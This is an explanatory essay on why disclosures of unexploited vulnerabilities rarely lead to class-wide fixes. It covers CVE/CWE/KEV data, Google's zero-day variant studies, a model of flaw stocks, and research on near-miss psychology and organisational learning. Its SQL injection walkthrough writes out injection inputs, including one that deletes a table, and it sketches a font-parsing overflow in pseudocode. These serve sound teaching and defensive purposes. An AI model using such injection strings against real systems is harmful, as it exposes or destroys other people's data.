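# Why near-miss disclosures rarely produce systemic fixes for an entire vulnerability class

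## What is a near-miss disclosure, and what counts as fixing a whole class?

A vulnerability is a flaw that an attacker could use to make a system do something its owner forbids, such as handing over another customer's records or running a stranger's program. Researchers, users and software makers find such flaws constantly, now often with AI, and makers repair many of them before anyone has seen an attacker use them. Security engineers commonly complain that makers repair only the reported flaw, and that the same kind of mistake soon produces another one elsewhere in the product or in someone else's. Nobody counts how many reports have led to the removal of a whole kind of mistake, so the complaint can only be judged on indirect evidence. The judgment also depends a good deal on what counts as a near miss and what counts as a fix.

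### Flaws, attacks and the three catalogues

An exploit is code or input that an attacker uses to take advantage of a vulnerability. A patch is an update from the product's maker that removes the vulnerability. A zero-day is a vulnerability that attackers exploit before the maker has issued a patch. To prevent this, many researchers follow coordinated vulnerability disclosure (CVD), in which they report a vulnerability privately to the maker and publish it after a patch is released or a deadline passes.

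Most published flaws end up in CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures), the public catalogue that gives each vulnerability its own identifier. The US government's Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) sponsors the catalogue, and MITRE, a non-profit that operates research centres for the government, runs it. Authorised organisations, many of them software makers, assign the identifiers. *CISA outlines improvement plan for CVE program* (Starks, 2026) reported that the contract behind the programme nearly ended in 2025. The number of new records is rising. The programme had published more than 67,000 in 2026 by mid-September, and *CISA's CVE program shake-up* (O'Flaherty, 2026) gave a forecast of 96,000 for the full year.

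A second MITRE catalogue, CWE (Common Weakness Enumeration), lists kinds of mistake. According to MITRE's *Twenty Years of Community-Developed Cybersecurity Weakness Knowledge*, the first public draft appeared in March 2006 and grew out of an earlier exercise in which researchers sorted more than 1,500 CVE records into roughly 290 types. The CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2024) defines a vulnerability as an instance of one or more weaknesses in a product. MITRE's *CWE Glossary* defines a weakness as a condition that could contribute to the introduction of vulnerabilities. A vulnerability class consists of all the flaws that arise from the same kind of mistake.

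CISA keeps a much shorter list, the Known Exploited Vulnerabilities (KEV) catalogue. To be listed, a flaw needs a CVE identifier, reliable evidence that someone has exploited it, and a clear action for users to take, such as installing an update. CISA's *Reducing the Significant Risk of Known Exploited Vulnerabilities* counts failed attempts as exploitation, but not a proof of concept (the demonstration code that researchers pass to makers to show that a flaw is real) or scanning for vulnerable machines.

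The catalogues are linked. In August 2025, for example, CISA added CVE-2025-57819, a flaw in the telephone software FreePBX, to its *Known Exploited Vulnerabilities Catalog*. The entry links the flaw to CWE-89, the identifier for SQL injection, which is the class in the worked example below.

### Why "near miss" is an imperfect term

The term "near miss" comes from the study of industrial accidents and has only recently reached cybersecurity law. The European Union's *Directive (EU) 2022/2555* (2022), usually known as NIS2, defines a near miss as an event that could have compromised data or services "but that was successfully prevented from materialising or that did not materialise". An incident is an event that does compromise them. The directive treats a vulnerability as a property of a product or service rather than an event, defining it as a weakness, susceptibility or flaw that a cyber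 threat can exploit.

At Leiden University, van Steen, Wolbers and Del-Real (2026), in *Close Calls in Cyberspace*, sorted near misses by asking who or what prevented the harm, and whether by acting or by failing to act. That gives four categories:

- Human active. During the 2016 theft from Bangladesh's central bank, an employee of Deutsche Bank saw "fandation" where a payment order should have read "foundation", and queried it. The question exposed the fraud and prevented further losses of about $850 million or more.
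- Human passive. An employee believes a fraudulent email but is too busy to answer it, and then forgets about it.
- System active. Antivirus software detects a virus and isolates it.
- System passive. An attacker writes malware for the newest version of a program, and the victim's update has failed, so the malware does not work.

Each of these categories starts with an attack. When a researcher finds a flaw by reading code and reports it, there may be no attacker. The closest category is the human active one, since a person notices something and acts on it, but no attack was under way for that person to stop. A mechanic who finds a crack in a wing during an inspection has not had a near miss in the sense that two pilots have when their aircraft pass too close.

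The term is still worth borrowing. Van Steen and colleagues give as a reason for studying near misses that they cost less to learn from than incidents do. A report of an unexploited flaw has the same advantage, because the maker learns about a mistake without anyone's data having been stolen. Here, a near-miss disclosure is a report of a vulnerability that, as far as anyone knows at the time, no attacker has exploited.

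The words "as far as anyone knows" matter there because attacks often leave no clear traces, as van Steen and colleagues point out. They cite an IBM figure of 181 days as the average time before an organisation discovers a data breach. The news site SecurityWeek found that some flaws in CISA's catalogue seemed to have no public report of any attack, although CISA had confirmed that attackers had exploited all of them. An outsider relying on public reports would have wrongly classed those flaws as near misses.

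Exploitation can also begin after the disclosure. CISA notes that publishing a proof of concept can make an attack more likely. A flaw in Adminer, a tool for managing databases, has an identifier from 2021, but CISA added it to the catalogue only on 29 September 2025. The listing date doesn't show when the first attack happened. Attackers may have ignored the flaw for four years, or CISA may have lacked good enough evidence until then.

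CISA counts an attempted exploit on a honeypot, a decoy machine that defenders set up to observe intruders, as exploitation, so the flaw qualifies for the catalogue if it meets the other criteria. Under the European definition, though, an attack that fails to do harm is close to a textbook near miss.

Still, near-miss disclosures are probably the ordinary case. CISA's catalogue of exploited flaws held 1,422 entries at the end of September 2025, accumulated over several years, while tens of thousands of CVE records now appear in a single year. The catalogue undercounts because CISA leaves out exploited flaws for which users have no clear remedy and relies partly on outsiders to report them. But the undercount would have to be enormous for near misses not to be the ordinary case.

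### One flaw and five responses to it

Many programs keep their records in a database and query it in a language called SQL. The following lines, simplified from an example in MITRE's *CWE-89*, let a customer of an online shop search through past orders:

```
customer = name_of_logged_in_user()
product  = text_from_search_box()
query    = "SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = '" + customer
           + "' AND product = '" + product + "'"
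run(query)
```

If a customer called Ana types `pen`, the program joins the pieces into this query, and the database returns Ana's orders for pens:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = 'ana' AND product = 'pen'
```

Now suppose Ana types `pen' OR 'a'='a` instead. The query becomes:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = 'ana' AND product = 'pen' OR 'a'='a'
```

The apostrophe after `pen` closes the quoted text early, so the database treats the rest of what Ana typed as part of the command. SQL groups AND before OR, so the condition now covers any row where the customer is Ana and the product is a pen, or where the letter a equals itself. The second half is true of every row, so Ana sees everybody's orders. Many database servers also accept several commands in one string. On those, typing `pen'; DELETE FROM orders; --` would delete every row in the table. The two hyphens turn the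 leftover apostrophe into a comment. This attack is called SQL injection, and it works because the program mixes outside text into a command and the database cannot distinguish the two.

Say a researcher reports the flaw in the search box to the shop before anyone has abused it. The shop could respond in at least five ways.

1. Fix that query. A programmer changes this one line, for example by escaping the apostrophes in `product`, which means marking them so that the database reads them as ordinary characters. Ana's trick stops working in the search box. If the page for looking up invoices joins its query in the same way, that page is as open as before.

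2. Search for variants. A variant is a flaw closely related to one already reported, such as the same mistake reached by another path. The programmer looks through the code for every query that includes outside text, and repairs the invoice page along with whatever else turns up.

3. Add a filter. The shop rejects or strips suspicious characters in everything that customers type, or puts a firewall in front of the site to block requests that resemble attacks. MITRE is unenthusiastic about both. A customer named O'Reilly has a legitimate apostrophe, and a filter that strips it records the wrong name. Attackers can aim at fields that the query does not put in quotation marks: where a program expects an order number, `5 OR 1=1` does the damage without a single apostrophe. As for application firewalls, MITRE rates their effectiveness as moderate, since they may not cover every route into the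 program and malformed input can slip past them.

4. Offer a safe query interface. The usual one is the parameterised query, in which the programmer writes the command with gaps and supplies the values separately:

```
run("SELECT * FROM orders WHERE customer = ? AND product = ?",
    customer, product)
```

The database parses the command before any value goes into it, so if Ana types the malicious text, the database searches for a product with that name and finds none.

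5. Forbid the unsafe interface. The shop changes `run` so that it accepts only command text that a programmer has written out in full in the source code. A query with outside text joined into it no longer builds, so it never reaches a customer. Google enforces rules of this sort in its own code.

Repairing one query is an instance fix, which removes one reported flaw and leaves the rest of the class in place. Finding and repairing variants removes more flaws, sometimes many more, but these are still instance fixes, because a programmer hired next week can make the same mistake on a new page. A class-level fix changes a language, interface, default or architecture so that a whole kind of flaw becomes impossible or very rare, as forbidding the unsafe interface does.

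Offering a safe interface counts as fixing the whole class only if nearly everyone uses it and somebody converts the old queries, and neither happens just because the interface exists. For example, in its catalogue entry on SQL injection, MITRE recommends database layers such as Hibernate, which can give significant protection "if used properly". But the same catalogue has a narrower entry, CWE-564, for SQL injection in programs that use Hibernate. MITRE also warns that programmers can bring the flaw back by assembling query strings inside the safe features.

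Even a ban may need exceptions, because some programs have to build commands as they run. One example is a reporting tool that lets users choose their own columns, and MITRE accepts that mixing commands and data may sometimes be unavoidable. A team with such a tool would need a reviewed exception to its rule, and could then claim to have made SQL injection very rare in its code, but not impossible.

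### Eliminating a class and mitigating it

People use "mitigation" loosely. MITRE's entry lists everything from parameterised queries to firewalls under that heading, while CISA reserves the word for temporary measures that users can take to prevent exploitation. The question of class-wide fixes calls for a narrower sense than MITRE's, in which a mitigation leaves flaws in place but makes them harder to exploit or less harmful. The filter is one example, and restricting the program's privileges is a clearer one. If the shop's search page connects to the database through an account that can read orders but not delete them, Ana's DELETE command fails, but the `OR 'a'='a'` trick still works because it only needs to read orders.

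Mitigations can still be a reasonable choice. An organization that cannot change a supplier's code may have no better option, and one that can may be able to install a filter in an afternoon while it still has old queries to convert. But mitigations can reduce successful attacks while programmers keep introducing flaws at the same rate, so a fall in attacks does not by itself show that a vulnerability class is going away.

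### How wide is a class?

CWE arranges weaknesses in four levels, which MITRE's glossary calls, from most to least abstract, pillars, classes, bases and variants. Both "class" and "variant" are technical terms in CWE. A CWE variant is a weakness specific to a particular type of product or technology, whereas the variants a programmer looks for after a report are individual flaws. SQL injection is a base. It falls under CWE-943, which covers improper handling of special characters in data queries of any kind, and, in another of MITRE's arrangements, under CWE-74, which covers injection in general. The Hibernate entry falls under SQL injection.

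Whether the shop has fixed the class therefore depends on which of these is meant. Banning joined queries removes SQL injection from its code almost entirely. It does not remove injection in general, because the same program may still paste a customer's text into an operating system command. That mistake is fairly common. The flaws CISA listed in September 2025 included a command injection in TP-Link home routers and another in a Libraesva email security product, which an attacker could trigger with a compressed attachment.

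The same choice comes up with memory safety, which means that a program can only read and write memory it is entitled to use at that moment. Two other entries from that month were a use of already freed memory in Android and a write past the end of a buffer in Cisco's network software. They belong to different classes in a narrow classification, but both are memory safety failures in a broad one. A tool that caught every use of freed memory would eliminate that narrow class but only reduce the broad one.

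A vulnerability class can also span software from many organizations. In 2008, according to MITRE, attackers compromised a large number of web servers with a single SQL injection string that worked against many programs. If one company had banned queries built by joining strings, the ban would have protected only that company's code.

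## Does patching individual flaws wear a class down?

Each instance fix removes a flaw, so enough fixes might in principle eliminate a class even if nobody changes the language or the interface. Whether that happens depends on how quickly programmers add new flaws of the same kind. Patching seems to reduce the number of flaws in old code over a period of years, but new code adds more. The evidence comes from lists of flaws that attackers have exploited, Google's records of zero-days, and a few studies of how long flaws remain in code.

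### The same kinds of mistake, year after year

In August 2026 CISA published a review of vulnerabilities from US fiscal years 2024 and 2025. According to Help Net Security's *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (2026), 41.5% of KEV catalogue entries map to what MITRE calls "stubborn weaknesses". CISA also found that three of today's ten most common weaknesses would have counted as "unforgivable" by a 2007 standard.

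These findings rest on different tests, and some press reports have merged them. Lagonsin (2026), in *CISA warns of persistent software flaws in exploits*, applied "unforgivable" to the 41.5%, but that figure is for the stubborn weaknesses.

MITRE ranks weaknesses every year in its CWE Top 25 by how many CVE records each accounts for and how severe those flaws are. MITRE's *Stubborn Weaknesses in the CWE Top 25* (2023) lists 15 that appeared in every edition from 2019 to 2023, including SQL injection, use of freed memory and hard-coded passwords. CISA may have used a slightly different set, since Help Net Security describes weaknesses that made the list "nearly every year since 2019". If the 41.5% refers to all 1,422 entries in the catalogue at the end of September 2025, that is about 590 flaws.

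This is not strong evidence that patching fails, because a ranking is relative. The Top 25 always has 25 members, so a weakness can become half as common and keep its place if the others decline too. Common kinds of mistake will also make up a large share of exploited flaws because they are common. To show that attackers favour them, CISA would have to compare the 41.5% with the same weaknesses' share of all CVE records.

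In MITRE's rankings, the general entry for reading or writing outside a memory buffer fell from first place in 2019 to 17th in 2023, which MITRE called encouraging. But the narrower entry for writing outside a buffer ranked first in 2023, so part of the fall may have happened because analysts had started to choose more specific labels.

Labelling problems also make it harder to compare rankings of exploited weaknesses. *What CISA's FY2024-2025 Vulnerability Review Means for Runtime Security* (Gale, 2026) reported that CISA found improper input validation, a broad label for failing to check data from outside, to be the most frequent weakness in the KEV catalogue. That label doesn't appear in the ranking of exploited weaknesses in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 10 KEV Weaknesses List Insights* (2026). Neither does SQL injection, although CISA named it as one of six main drivers of real compromises and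 MITRE ranked it second in the general Top 25. MITRE looked at only 182 records and weighted them by severity, which may explain some of the difference. It also warned that some exploited flaws have labels that are too general, and that others have descriptions too thin to support an accurate label.

The 2007 standard comes from Christey (2007), in *Unforgivable Vulnerabilities*, written at MITRE. It has five criteria:

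1. Precedence. Many other developers, including well-known companies, have already made the mistake.
2. Documentation. Books, papers and articles explain the problem.
3. Obviousness. Anyone who thinks about possible attacks will see it immediately.
4. Attack simplicity. The standard attack works, such as typing a long row of the letter A to overflow a buffer.
5. Found in five. A tester could find the flaw within five minutes.

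An unforgivable flaw meets the first two criteria and at least two of the others. Christey meant this as a test of individual flaws. A login page that a single apostrophe can break fails badly, whereas an elaborate injection that gets past a competent filter may be forgivable. CISA's "three of the ten" extends the test to whole kinds of weakness. Still, it is hard to blame their survival on ignorance when textbooks explained them two decades ago. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre adopted the term "unforgivable" in *A method to assess 'forgivable' vs 'unforgivable' vulnerabilities* for flaws that are trivial to find and keep recurring.

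Christey also described how a typical product's flaws change as it ages, drawing on more than 25,000 CVE records. Researchers first find obvious flaws in the main features. Rushed patches protect one input but leave neighbouring inputs open, and then variants appear that bypass simple filters. Later, the developers eliminate the most common kinds of flaw, typically by reviewing the code systematically or rebuilding its input checks. After that, researchers mostly find rarer kinds.

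A class can disappear from a product, but in Christey's account that takes a systematic effort, not just individual patches. The account also suggests that an industry-wide list might hardly change while individual products improve, because each new type of product can repeat the old mistakes. In 2007 Christey placed leading web servers near the end of the sequence and many internet telephony products near the start.

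The KEV catalogue is also a selected sample. Gale cited the security company VulnCheck, which found evidence of exploitation for 884 flaws in 2025, while CISA added 245 to its catalogue that year. Gale's employer, Oligo, sells software that blocks attacks on running programs, so it has some interest in the catalogue looking incomplete. But MITRE gave a technical reason to expect gaps. In cross-site request forgery, a malicious link makes a logged-in user's browser send a request the user never intended. Part of the attack happens outside the victim's network, where defenders' monitoring may miss it. This weakness ranked third in the general Top 25 but is missing from the exploited top ten, and nobody knows how much of that difference reflects attackers' preferences.

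Yearly additions don't measure progress any better. KBY Technologies' *CISA KEV 2026* (2026) gives 324 additions in 2026 up to 27 November, against 224 in 2025. The 224 probably covers only the same part of the year, since Gale's total for 2025 is 245. Attackers may be exploiting more flaws, or CISA may be confirming more of them. SecurityWeek also reported that 94 of the flaws added in 2025 had been disclosed in 2024 or earlier.

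### Zero-days that resemble earlier flaws

Project Zero, a Google team that looks for unknown flaws in widely used software, tried a more direct test. It checked whether each zero-day that attackers had been caught using was a variant of a flaw already reported. If it was, a more thorough repair the first time might have prevented the attack.

Stone (2021), in *A Year in Review of 0-days Exploited In-The-Wild in 2020*, classed 6 of the 24 zero-days from 2020 as variants. Stone (2022) found at least 9 variants out of 18 zero-days in the first half of 2022. Google's *The Ups and Downs of 0-days* (2023) counted 17 out of 41 for the whole year.

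Many of the earlier flaws were near misses. In Google's list for 2022, eight of the 17 variants followed a flaw that attackers had already used as a zero-day. Google noted no such history for the other nine, whose original flaws included a Firefox crash produced by automated testing and a bug in Safari's engine found when a test failed. In Stone's list for 2020, four of the six variants followed a flaw with no recorded exploitation. Across the two years, 13 of the 23 variants followed a flaw that, as far as Google knew, attackers had not exploited.

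One of those warnings concerned FreeType, a software library that Chrome uses to draw fonts. A font can contain small pictures. To load one, FreeType reads the width and height from the picture's header, calculates and reserves the memory it needs, and copies the picture in. In November 2014 Mateusz Jurczyk of Project Zero reported that, for very large pictures, the result of the calculation could be too big for the variable meant to hold it. FreeType then got a much smaller number and reserved too little memory. FreeType's developers added a check that rejected any picture more than 32,767 pixels wide or high.

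Unfortunately they put the check in the wrong place. The header stores the width as a 32-bit number, but by the time of the check FreeType had cut it down to 16 bits, which can't hold anything above 65,535. In simplified form, with a width chosen for illustration:

```
width = lowest_16_bits(header_width)     # 65,537 becomes 1
if width > 32767: reject the picture     # 1 is fine
reserve memory for a picture of this width
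copy the picture in, using header_width  # runs past the end
```

In October 2020, Project Zero found attackers using this second route. The new patch moved the check up a few lines and applied it to the numbers in the header. Stone pointed out that the same check in 2014 would have closed both routes.

Microsoft made a similar mistake with splwow64, a Windows component that helps older programs to print. Internet Explorer ran with few privileges and could send messages to splwow64, which had more. One type of message, number 0x75, let the sender choose the source, destination and length of a copy within splwow64's memory. Attackers exploited this in 2019 and did the same with message type 0x6D in 2020. Microsoft's patch for the second attack replaced the memory addresses in the message with offsets (distances from a starting point), but attackers could choose harmful offsets just as easily.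 Someone sent Microsoft a working demonstration of this in September 2020. The fuller patch, in January 2021, checked that every copy stayed inside the message's own memory, a check the code should have made from the start. Even the 2019 attacks, which were more than a near miss, had not led Microsoft to repair the cause.

Internet Explorer's old scripting engine had an even longer series of related flaws. The engine's garbage collector, which frees memory that a script no longer needs, failed to track certain variables and freed memory that was still in use. Between December 2018 and January 2020, researchers caught attackers exploiting four flaws of this kind with the same technique, and Google attributed all four exploits to one group. The demonstration code for one flaw still worked after Microsoft patched it. Microsoft patched a fifth such flaw in April 2020.

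Later edits can also undo a thorough fix for an individual flaw. In 2013 the developers of Safari's engine fixed a use of freed memory by changing every route to the flaw, including routes that nobody had demonstrated, and they added a test. Stone (2022) traced how a programmer reversed part of that fix in December 2016 while tidying up code across 95 files. The flaw then stayed in the code for five years, until Apple patched it as a zero-day in January 2022. The 2013 test did not catch the flaw because it exercised a different route. Nothing in the language or the interface stopped the programmer from repeating the old mistake.

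The variant counts need some care, partly because what counts as a variant is a judgment. Stone's six for 2020 include a Safari flaw related to one in Microsoft's separate version of some Adobe font code, which Apple had no clear duty to monitor. Stone also doubted that attackers had exploited the Firefox flaw on the list. Google listed four possible reasons for the rise from a quarter to over 40%: defenders had become better at recognising variants, defenders had become better at catching attacks that used them, attackers were using more of them, or makers were patching less thoroughly. Google thought it was probably a mixture. With samples of 24 and 41, chance could also account for the difference.

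A more serious problem with the method is that Project Zero started from successful attacks and looked back, so its count leaves out any patch that closed every route and prevented an attack. The figures show a good deal about where zero-days come from, but not what proportion of patches are incomplete.

They are also several years old. *Look What You Made Us Patch*, Google's review of 2025 by Charrier, Sadowski and colleagues (2026), counted 90 zero-days, against 78 in 2024 and 100 in 2023. Roughly 35% were memory safety failures. Browsers accounted for less than 10%, down from 15 of the 41 in 2022. Charrier and colleagues credited measures that make browsers harder to exploit, though they added that attackers had become better at hiding. Under either explanation, the decline doesn't show that patching had used up the flaws in browsers.

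### How new flaws replace old ones

A simple model helps to explain why patching can go on for decades without exhausting a class. Suppose programmers introduce *r* new flaws of one class each year, and a flaw survives for *T* years on average before someone finds and repairs it. Suppose also that people are equally likely to find any of the flaws that remain. If there are *N* flaws in the code, people repair *N/T* of them a year, and the stock changes at the rate

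dN/dt = r − N/T

The stock stops changing when repairs keep pace with new flaws, which happens at N = rT. If programmers stop introducing flaws altogether, *r* is zero, and a stock that starts at N₀ shrinks as

N(t) = N₀ · exp(−t/T)

Say a company's programmers add 100 flaws a year (an invented figure) and each lasts 2.5 years on average. The company then has a steady stock of 250 flaws. It could hire enough searchers to double the rate of discovery, which would halve the average lifetime, *T*, to 1.25 years. Or it could make the mistake impossible in new code and keep searching at the old rate.

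| What the company does | Stock after 1 year | After 5 years | In the long run |
|---|---|---|---|
| Carries on as before | 250 | 250 | 250 |
| Doubles the rate of discovery | 181 | 127 | 125 |
| Stops new flaws from entering | 168 | 34 | 0 |
| Does both | 112 | 5 | 0 |

Doubling the search effort halves the stock to 125, but the stock then stays there, and it climbs back towards 250 if the company lets the extra searchers go. Getting down to 25 by searching alone would take ten times the original rate of discovery. Once new flaws stop coming in, however, the ordinary pace of repair is enough to wear the stock away. Memory safety flaws in Android fell in roughly this way after Google started writing much of its new code in safer languages.

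In this model, looking for variants has the same effect as searching harder. A maker that fixes one additional flaw for every flaw reported halves *T* without needing more reports. Bad patches have the opposite effect. In 2019 researchers reported a flaw in Chrome's JavaScript engine. Stone recounts that the first patch missed some of the routes to it and the next introduced a new vulnerability. If one patch in five fails or creates another flaw of the same class, the steady stock rises from 250 to about 313.

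The model also shows why the number of reports is a poor guide to how many flaws remain. When the company doubles its rate of discovery, the number of flaws found each year rises from 100 to about 169 in the first year, falls to 131 in the second, and then sinks back towards 100. Reports rise while the stock of flaws is shrinking, then return to their old level even though the stock has halved. According to Gale, the set of CVE records that CISA analysed grew from 14,234 in fiscal 2024 to 30,517 in fiscal 2025, and CISA attributed part of the growth to faster discovery with AI. Such a jump could equally mean that code is getting worse or that people are clearing a backlog.

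Some flaws are much easier to find than others, so people find the easy ones first, and the rest take longer than the formula predicts. The amount of code also grows. If programmers make the same number of mistakes per thousand lines and write more lines each year, *r* rises, and eventually so does the stock, however quickly people search.

### Do flaws run out?

Researchers have disagreed for two decades about whether fixing individual flaws noticeably reduces the number that remain. Eric Rescorla's *Is Finding Security Holes a Good Idea?* (2005) makes the sceptical case. Publishing a flaw does some harm, because attackers learn of it and target machines whose owners haven't installed the patch. That harm is justified if attackers would soon have found the flaw anyway, or if removing it leaves appreciably fewer to find. Rescorla found no clear sign that flaw reports became rarer as programs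 aged. If the supply of flaws is so large that fixing them barely reduces it, an attacker is also unlikely to find the same flaw as a friendly researcher, and much of the benefit of looking disappears.

Andy Ozment and Stuart Schechter reached a more hopeful result in *Milk or Wine* (2006). They studied seven and a half years and 15 versions of OpenBSD, an operating system whose developers audit its code for security. The public databases that Rescorla relied on show only roughly when a flaw entered a program. Ozment and Schechter worked out the dates from the code's history, which let them separate old flaws from new ones. Of the flaws reported during the study, 62% had been there from the beginning, and these were reported less often over time. But the decline was slow. The median lifetime of these original flaws was at least 2.6 years, which in the model above corresponds to a mean of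 about 3.75.

That study seems the better evidence on whether patching wears down old code, because it follows a fixed body of code instead of one that keeps growing. But it covers only one project, and an unusually careful one. A company that rarely audits its products might see a much smaller decline.

Nikolaos Alexopoulos and colleagues later measured lifetimes on a larger scale in *How Long Do Vulnerabilities Live in the Code?* (2022). Across several large open-source projects, a flaw lasted about four years on average, ranging from around two years in Chromium, the open-source basis for Chrome, to around seven in the encryption library OpenSSL. Lifetimes roughly followed the exponential pattern that the model assumes. By that formula, if no new flaws were added, 8% of the existing ones would remain after five years at Chromium's rate, 29% at the average rate and 49% at OpenSSL's. These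 percentages may be too low, since the study could only measure flaws that someone had found, and hidden ones may last longer.

Some of Google's observations count against Rescorla's other premise, that two people seldom find the same flaw. In 2022 Google saw more cases of separate attackers using the same vulnerability, and of researchers reporting flaws that later turned out to be known to attackers. Such overlap should be rare if the supply of flaws were practically endless. But Google could not measure how often it happens, and suggested that it might also occur because people read the same published research and then look in the same places. Google's evidence also comes mostly from popular consumer platforms, where many skilled people examine the same code. Rescorla's premise may well hold for an obscure industrial product.

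These findings concern the total number of flaws in a program, which can shrink without any one class getting close to zero. Alexopoulos and colleagues compared types of flaw and found no statistically significant difference in how long each type lasted within a given project. Their results therefore give no sign that repeated patching exhausts buffer overflows, for example, any sooner than other types. Neither they nor Ozment and Schechter followed individual disclosures to see what the developers did next, so we can't tell from their figures how often a report led anyone to change an interface or a language.

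## Why does a flaw that did no harm change so little inside an organisation?

A software maker's response to a vulnerability report depends partly on how its engineers and managers interpret a flaw that hurt nobody. Psychologists have studied reactions to narrow escapes since the 2000s, mostly in cases involving spacecraft, hurricanes and aircraft. Only one pair of experiments looked at computer users, so applying the other findings to software is an analogy.

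### Mistaking luck for good management

In *How Near-Misses Influence Decision Making Under Risk* (2008), Dillon and Tinsley asked students, NASA employees and contractors to rate a fictional project manager, Chris. *How to Avoid Catastrophe* (Tinsley, Dillon and Madsen, 2011) later described the set-up. Chris was short of time and skipped both a peer review and an investigation into a possible design flaw in an unmanned spacecraft. These decisions were the same in every version, but the outcome varied. Some participants read that the launch went well. Others read that the flaw caused a problem, but that the craft could keep sending data because the sun happened to be at the right angle. A third group read that the angle was wrong and the mission failed. Participants rated Chris about as highly after the lucky escape as after the successful launch, and gave different ratings only when the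 mission failed.

A second experiment put participants in charge of a rover on Mars with a sandstorm on the way. They learned that driving through a storm carried a 40% chance of wrecking the wheels. Half of them also learned that the rover had come through earlier storms unharmed. About three-quarters of that half chose to drive on, compared with 13% of the others.

Surviving several storms is some evidence that a rover is sturdy, which could justify the drivers' choice, but both groups still put the risk at 40% when asked. Dillon and Tinsley concluded that people with a lucky history felt safer without necessarily changing their estimate of the odds.

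Expertise doesn't seem to stop people from finding near misses reassuring. Newswise's *Disaster near misses can produce sense of security* summarised a 2011 study in which professional risk analysts, like members of the public, chose less flood insurance after a near miss, and sometimes none at all. According to PsyPost's *Cognitive psychology research suggests pilots could be learning the wrong lessons from close calls*, 142 pilots who read about flights into doubtful weather judged the close calls much as they judged the safe flights.

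A near miss can also make people more cautious. Tinsley, Dillon and Cronin (2012), in a study whose summary is reprinted in Schneier's *The Effects of Near Misses on Risk Decision-Making* (2015), tested decisions about evacuating a house, taking a Caribbean cruise in hurricane season and drilling for oil in deep water. People who saw a near miss as a disaster that did not occur took more risks afterwards, whereas people who saw it as a disaster that almost happened took more precautions. Dillon, in *Close encounters*, calls these "resilient" and "vulnerable" near misses, and thinks they change how bad people imagine the consequences would be more than how likely people think them. Dillon and Tinsley (2015) later found in an experiment, reported in *Near-miss events, risk messages, and decision making*, that a harmless near miss made people more optimistic in general, and that this optimism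 helped to explain why they took fewer precautions.

A vulnerability report could either alarm a company or reassure it. A researcher who includes a working demonstration shows the maker what an attacker could have done, which ought to make the flaw look like a disaster that almost happened. But the maker then announces that it knows of no attacks, and managers who read only the announcement may conclude that the company's defences are fine. Companies can choose the more alarming interpretation. Google, for example, investigated a memory flaw in CrabbyAVIF, an Android image library, as a near miss even though it had caught the flaw before release.

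Choices made in laboratory experiments may exaggerate the effect. Dillon cites a field study by Kirstin Dow and Susan Cutter of South Carolina residents who evacuated for Hurricane Bertha in 1996, when the storm went to North Carolina instead. When Hurricane Fran approached a few weeks later, the unnecessary evacuation played only a minor part in people's decisions about whether to leave again.

Rosoff, Cui and John (2013) ran the security experiments, reported in *Heuristics and Biases in Cyber Security Dilemmas*. Participants chose between safer and riskier responses to situations that an ordinary computer user might face. The first experiment varied whether participants had a near miss to look back on and whether the outcomes were described as gains or losses. The near miss led people to choose safer responses when the outcomes were described as gains. The second experiment described all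 outcomes as losses and compared three kinds of past experience. Participants who recalled losing data were the most cautious, followed by those who recalled a near miss and then those who recalled a false alarm.

The only direct evidence from security shows that people learn less from near misses than from real losses, but not that near misses make them careless. That evidence concerns individuals protecting their own computers, while a manager deciding whether to rewrite a product has other people's deadlines and money to consider.

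### What airlines learn from

Airlines are a closer comparison, because they are organisations with engineers, budgets and regulators. Madsen, Dillon and Tinsley (2016), in *Airline Safety Improvement Through Experience with Near‐Misses*, analysed US commercial airlines from 1990 to 2007. They compared each airline with its own record over time, so that permanent differences between airlines would not distort the result. Airlines improved after accidents, including other airlines' accidents. They also improved after near misses in which the danger was obvious, but not after other near misses.

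Georgetown University's *U.S. Airlines Learning from Accident Close Calls, But They Can Try Harder* gives two conditions for an airline to learn from a near miss. The event has to fit a recognised category, and people have to know that this category has caused accidents before. Otherwise, a risky practice can become routine. In March 2000 the pilots of a Southwest Airlines jet made a steep, fast approach of a kind that had worked before. The jet ran off a short runway at Burbank, California, crossed a street and stopped near a petrol station.

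SQL injection easily meets both conditions, since MITRE has given it a category and attackers have used it for decades. Yet the persistence of the "stubborn weaknesses" suggests that many software makers don't learn from near misses of this kind, although the airline results would lead us to expect them to. Failure to recognise the danger therefore can't be the main reason makers neglect a familiar class, though it may explain why they neglect an unfamiliar one.

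Managers can also affect whether an organisation recognises a near miss. BYU News' *What your company can learn from NASA's tragedies* reported that NASA recognised more near misses when leaders emphasised safety over other goals, such as efficiency, and when they stressed a project's significance. But someone still has to do the extra work after a near miss is recognised.

### Fixing the problem in front of you

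Tucker and Edmondson (2003), in *Why Hospitals Don't Learn from Failures*, watched 26 nurses for 239 hours at nine hospitals, mostly chosen for their reputation for excellent nursing. They saw 194 failures, of which 28 were errors, such as forgetting a patient's medicine, and 166 were problems that disrupted work, such as missing supplies or broken equipment.

Tucker and Edmondson distinguish two ways workers respond to problems. In first-order problem solving, a worker gets round the obstacle and carries on. One nurse who ran out of clean linen on a night shift took some from another unit. The patients got clean beds, but the other unit had less linen, and whoever was supposed to deliver the linen didn't learn about the shortage. In second-order problem solving, the worker also addresses the cause. When a new nurse left a specialised intensive-care bed on the cancer ward, a nurse there phoned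 the other unit's manager to explain the mistake so that it wouldn't happen again.

Nurses handled 93% of the problems by doing what the patient needed and no more. Only 7% of responses were second-order, even though Tucker and Edmondson counted any attempt to call attention to the problem. Workarounds took up an average of 33 minutes of each nurse's eight-hour shift. The nurses had patients waiting, and seven of the nine who discussed the subject in interviews found it gratifying to get round an obstacle. Tucker and Edmondson rejected low motivation and the difficulty of the problems as explanations for the lack of second-order responses.

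An instance fix is first-order problem solving in this sense. A programmer with a reported flaw and a deadline repairs the query and closes the report, which is what the customer urgently needs. One difference is that the flaw has already reached the right people. A researcher who reports a flaw to the software's maker has done second-order work by Tucker and Edmondson's generous standard. In software, the process more often stalls at the next step, when the maker decides how much to do with the information.

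Prevention also earns little credit. *Nobody Ever Gets Credit for Fixing Problems that Never Happened* (Repenning and Sterman, 2001) argues that an organisation under pressure can either work harder or improve how it works. Working harder raises output at once, while improvement takes time away from output now and brings benefits later, so managers cut improvement first. The damage from cutting it also appears later. A follow-up, *The Capability Trap*, describes the resulting spiral, in which performance falls as maintenance and learning decline, increasing the pressure to work harder and leaving even less time for improvement.

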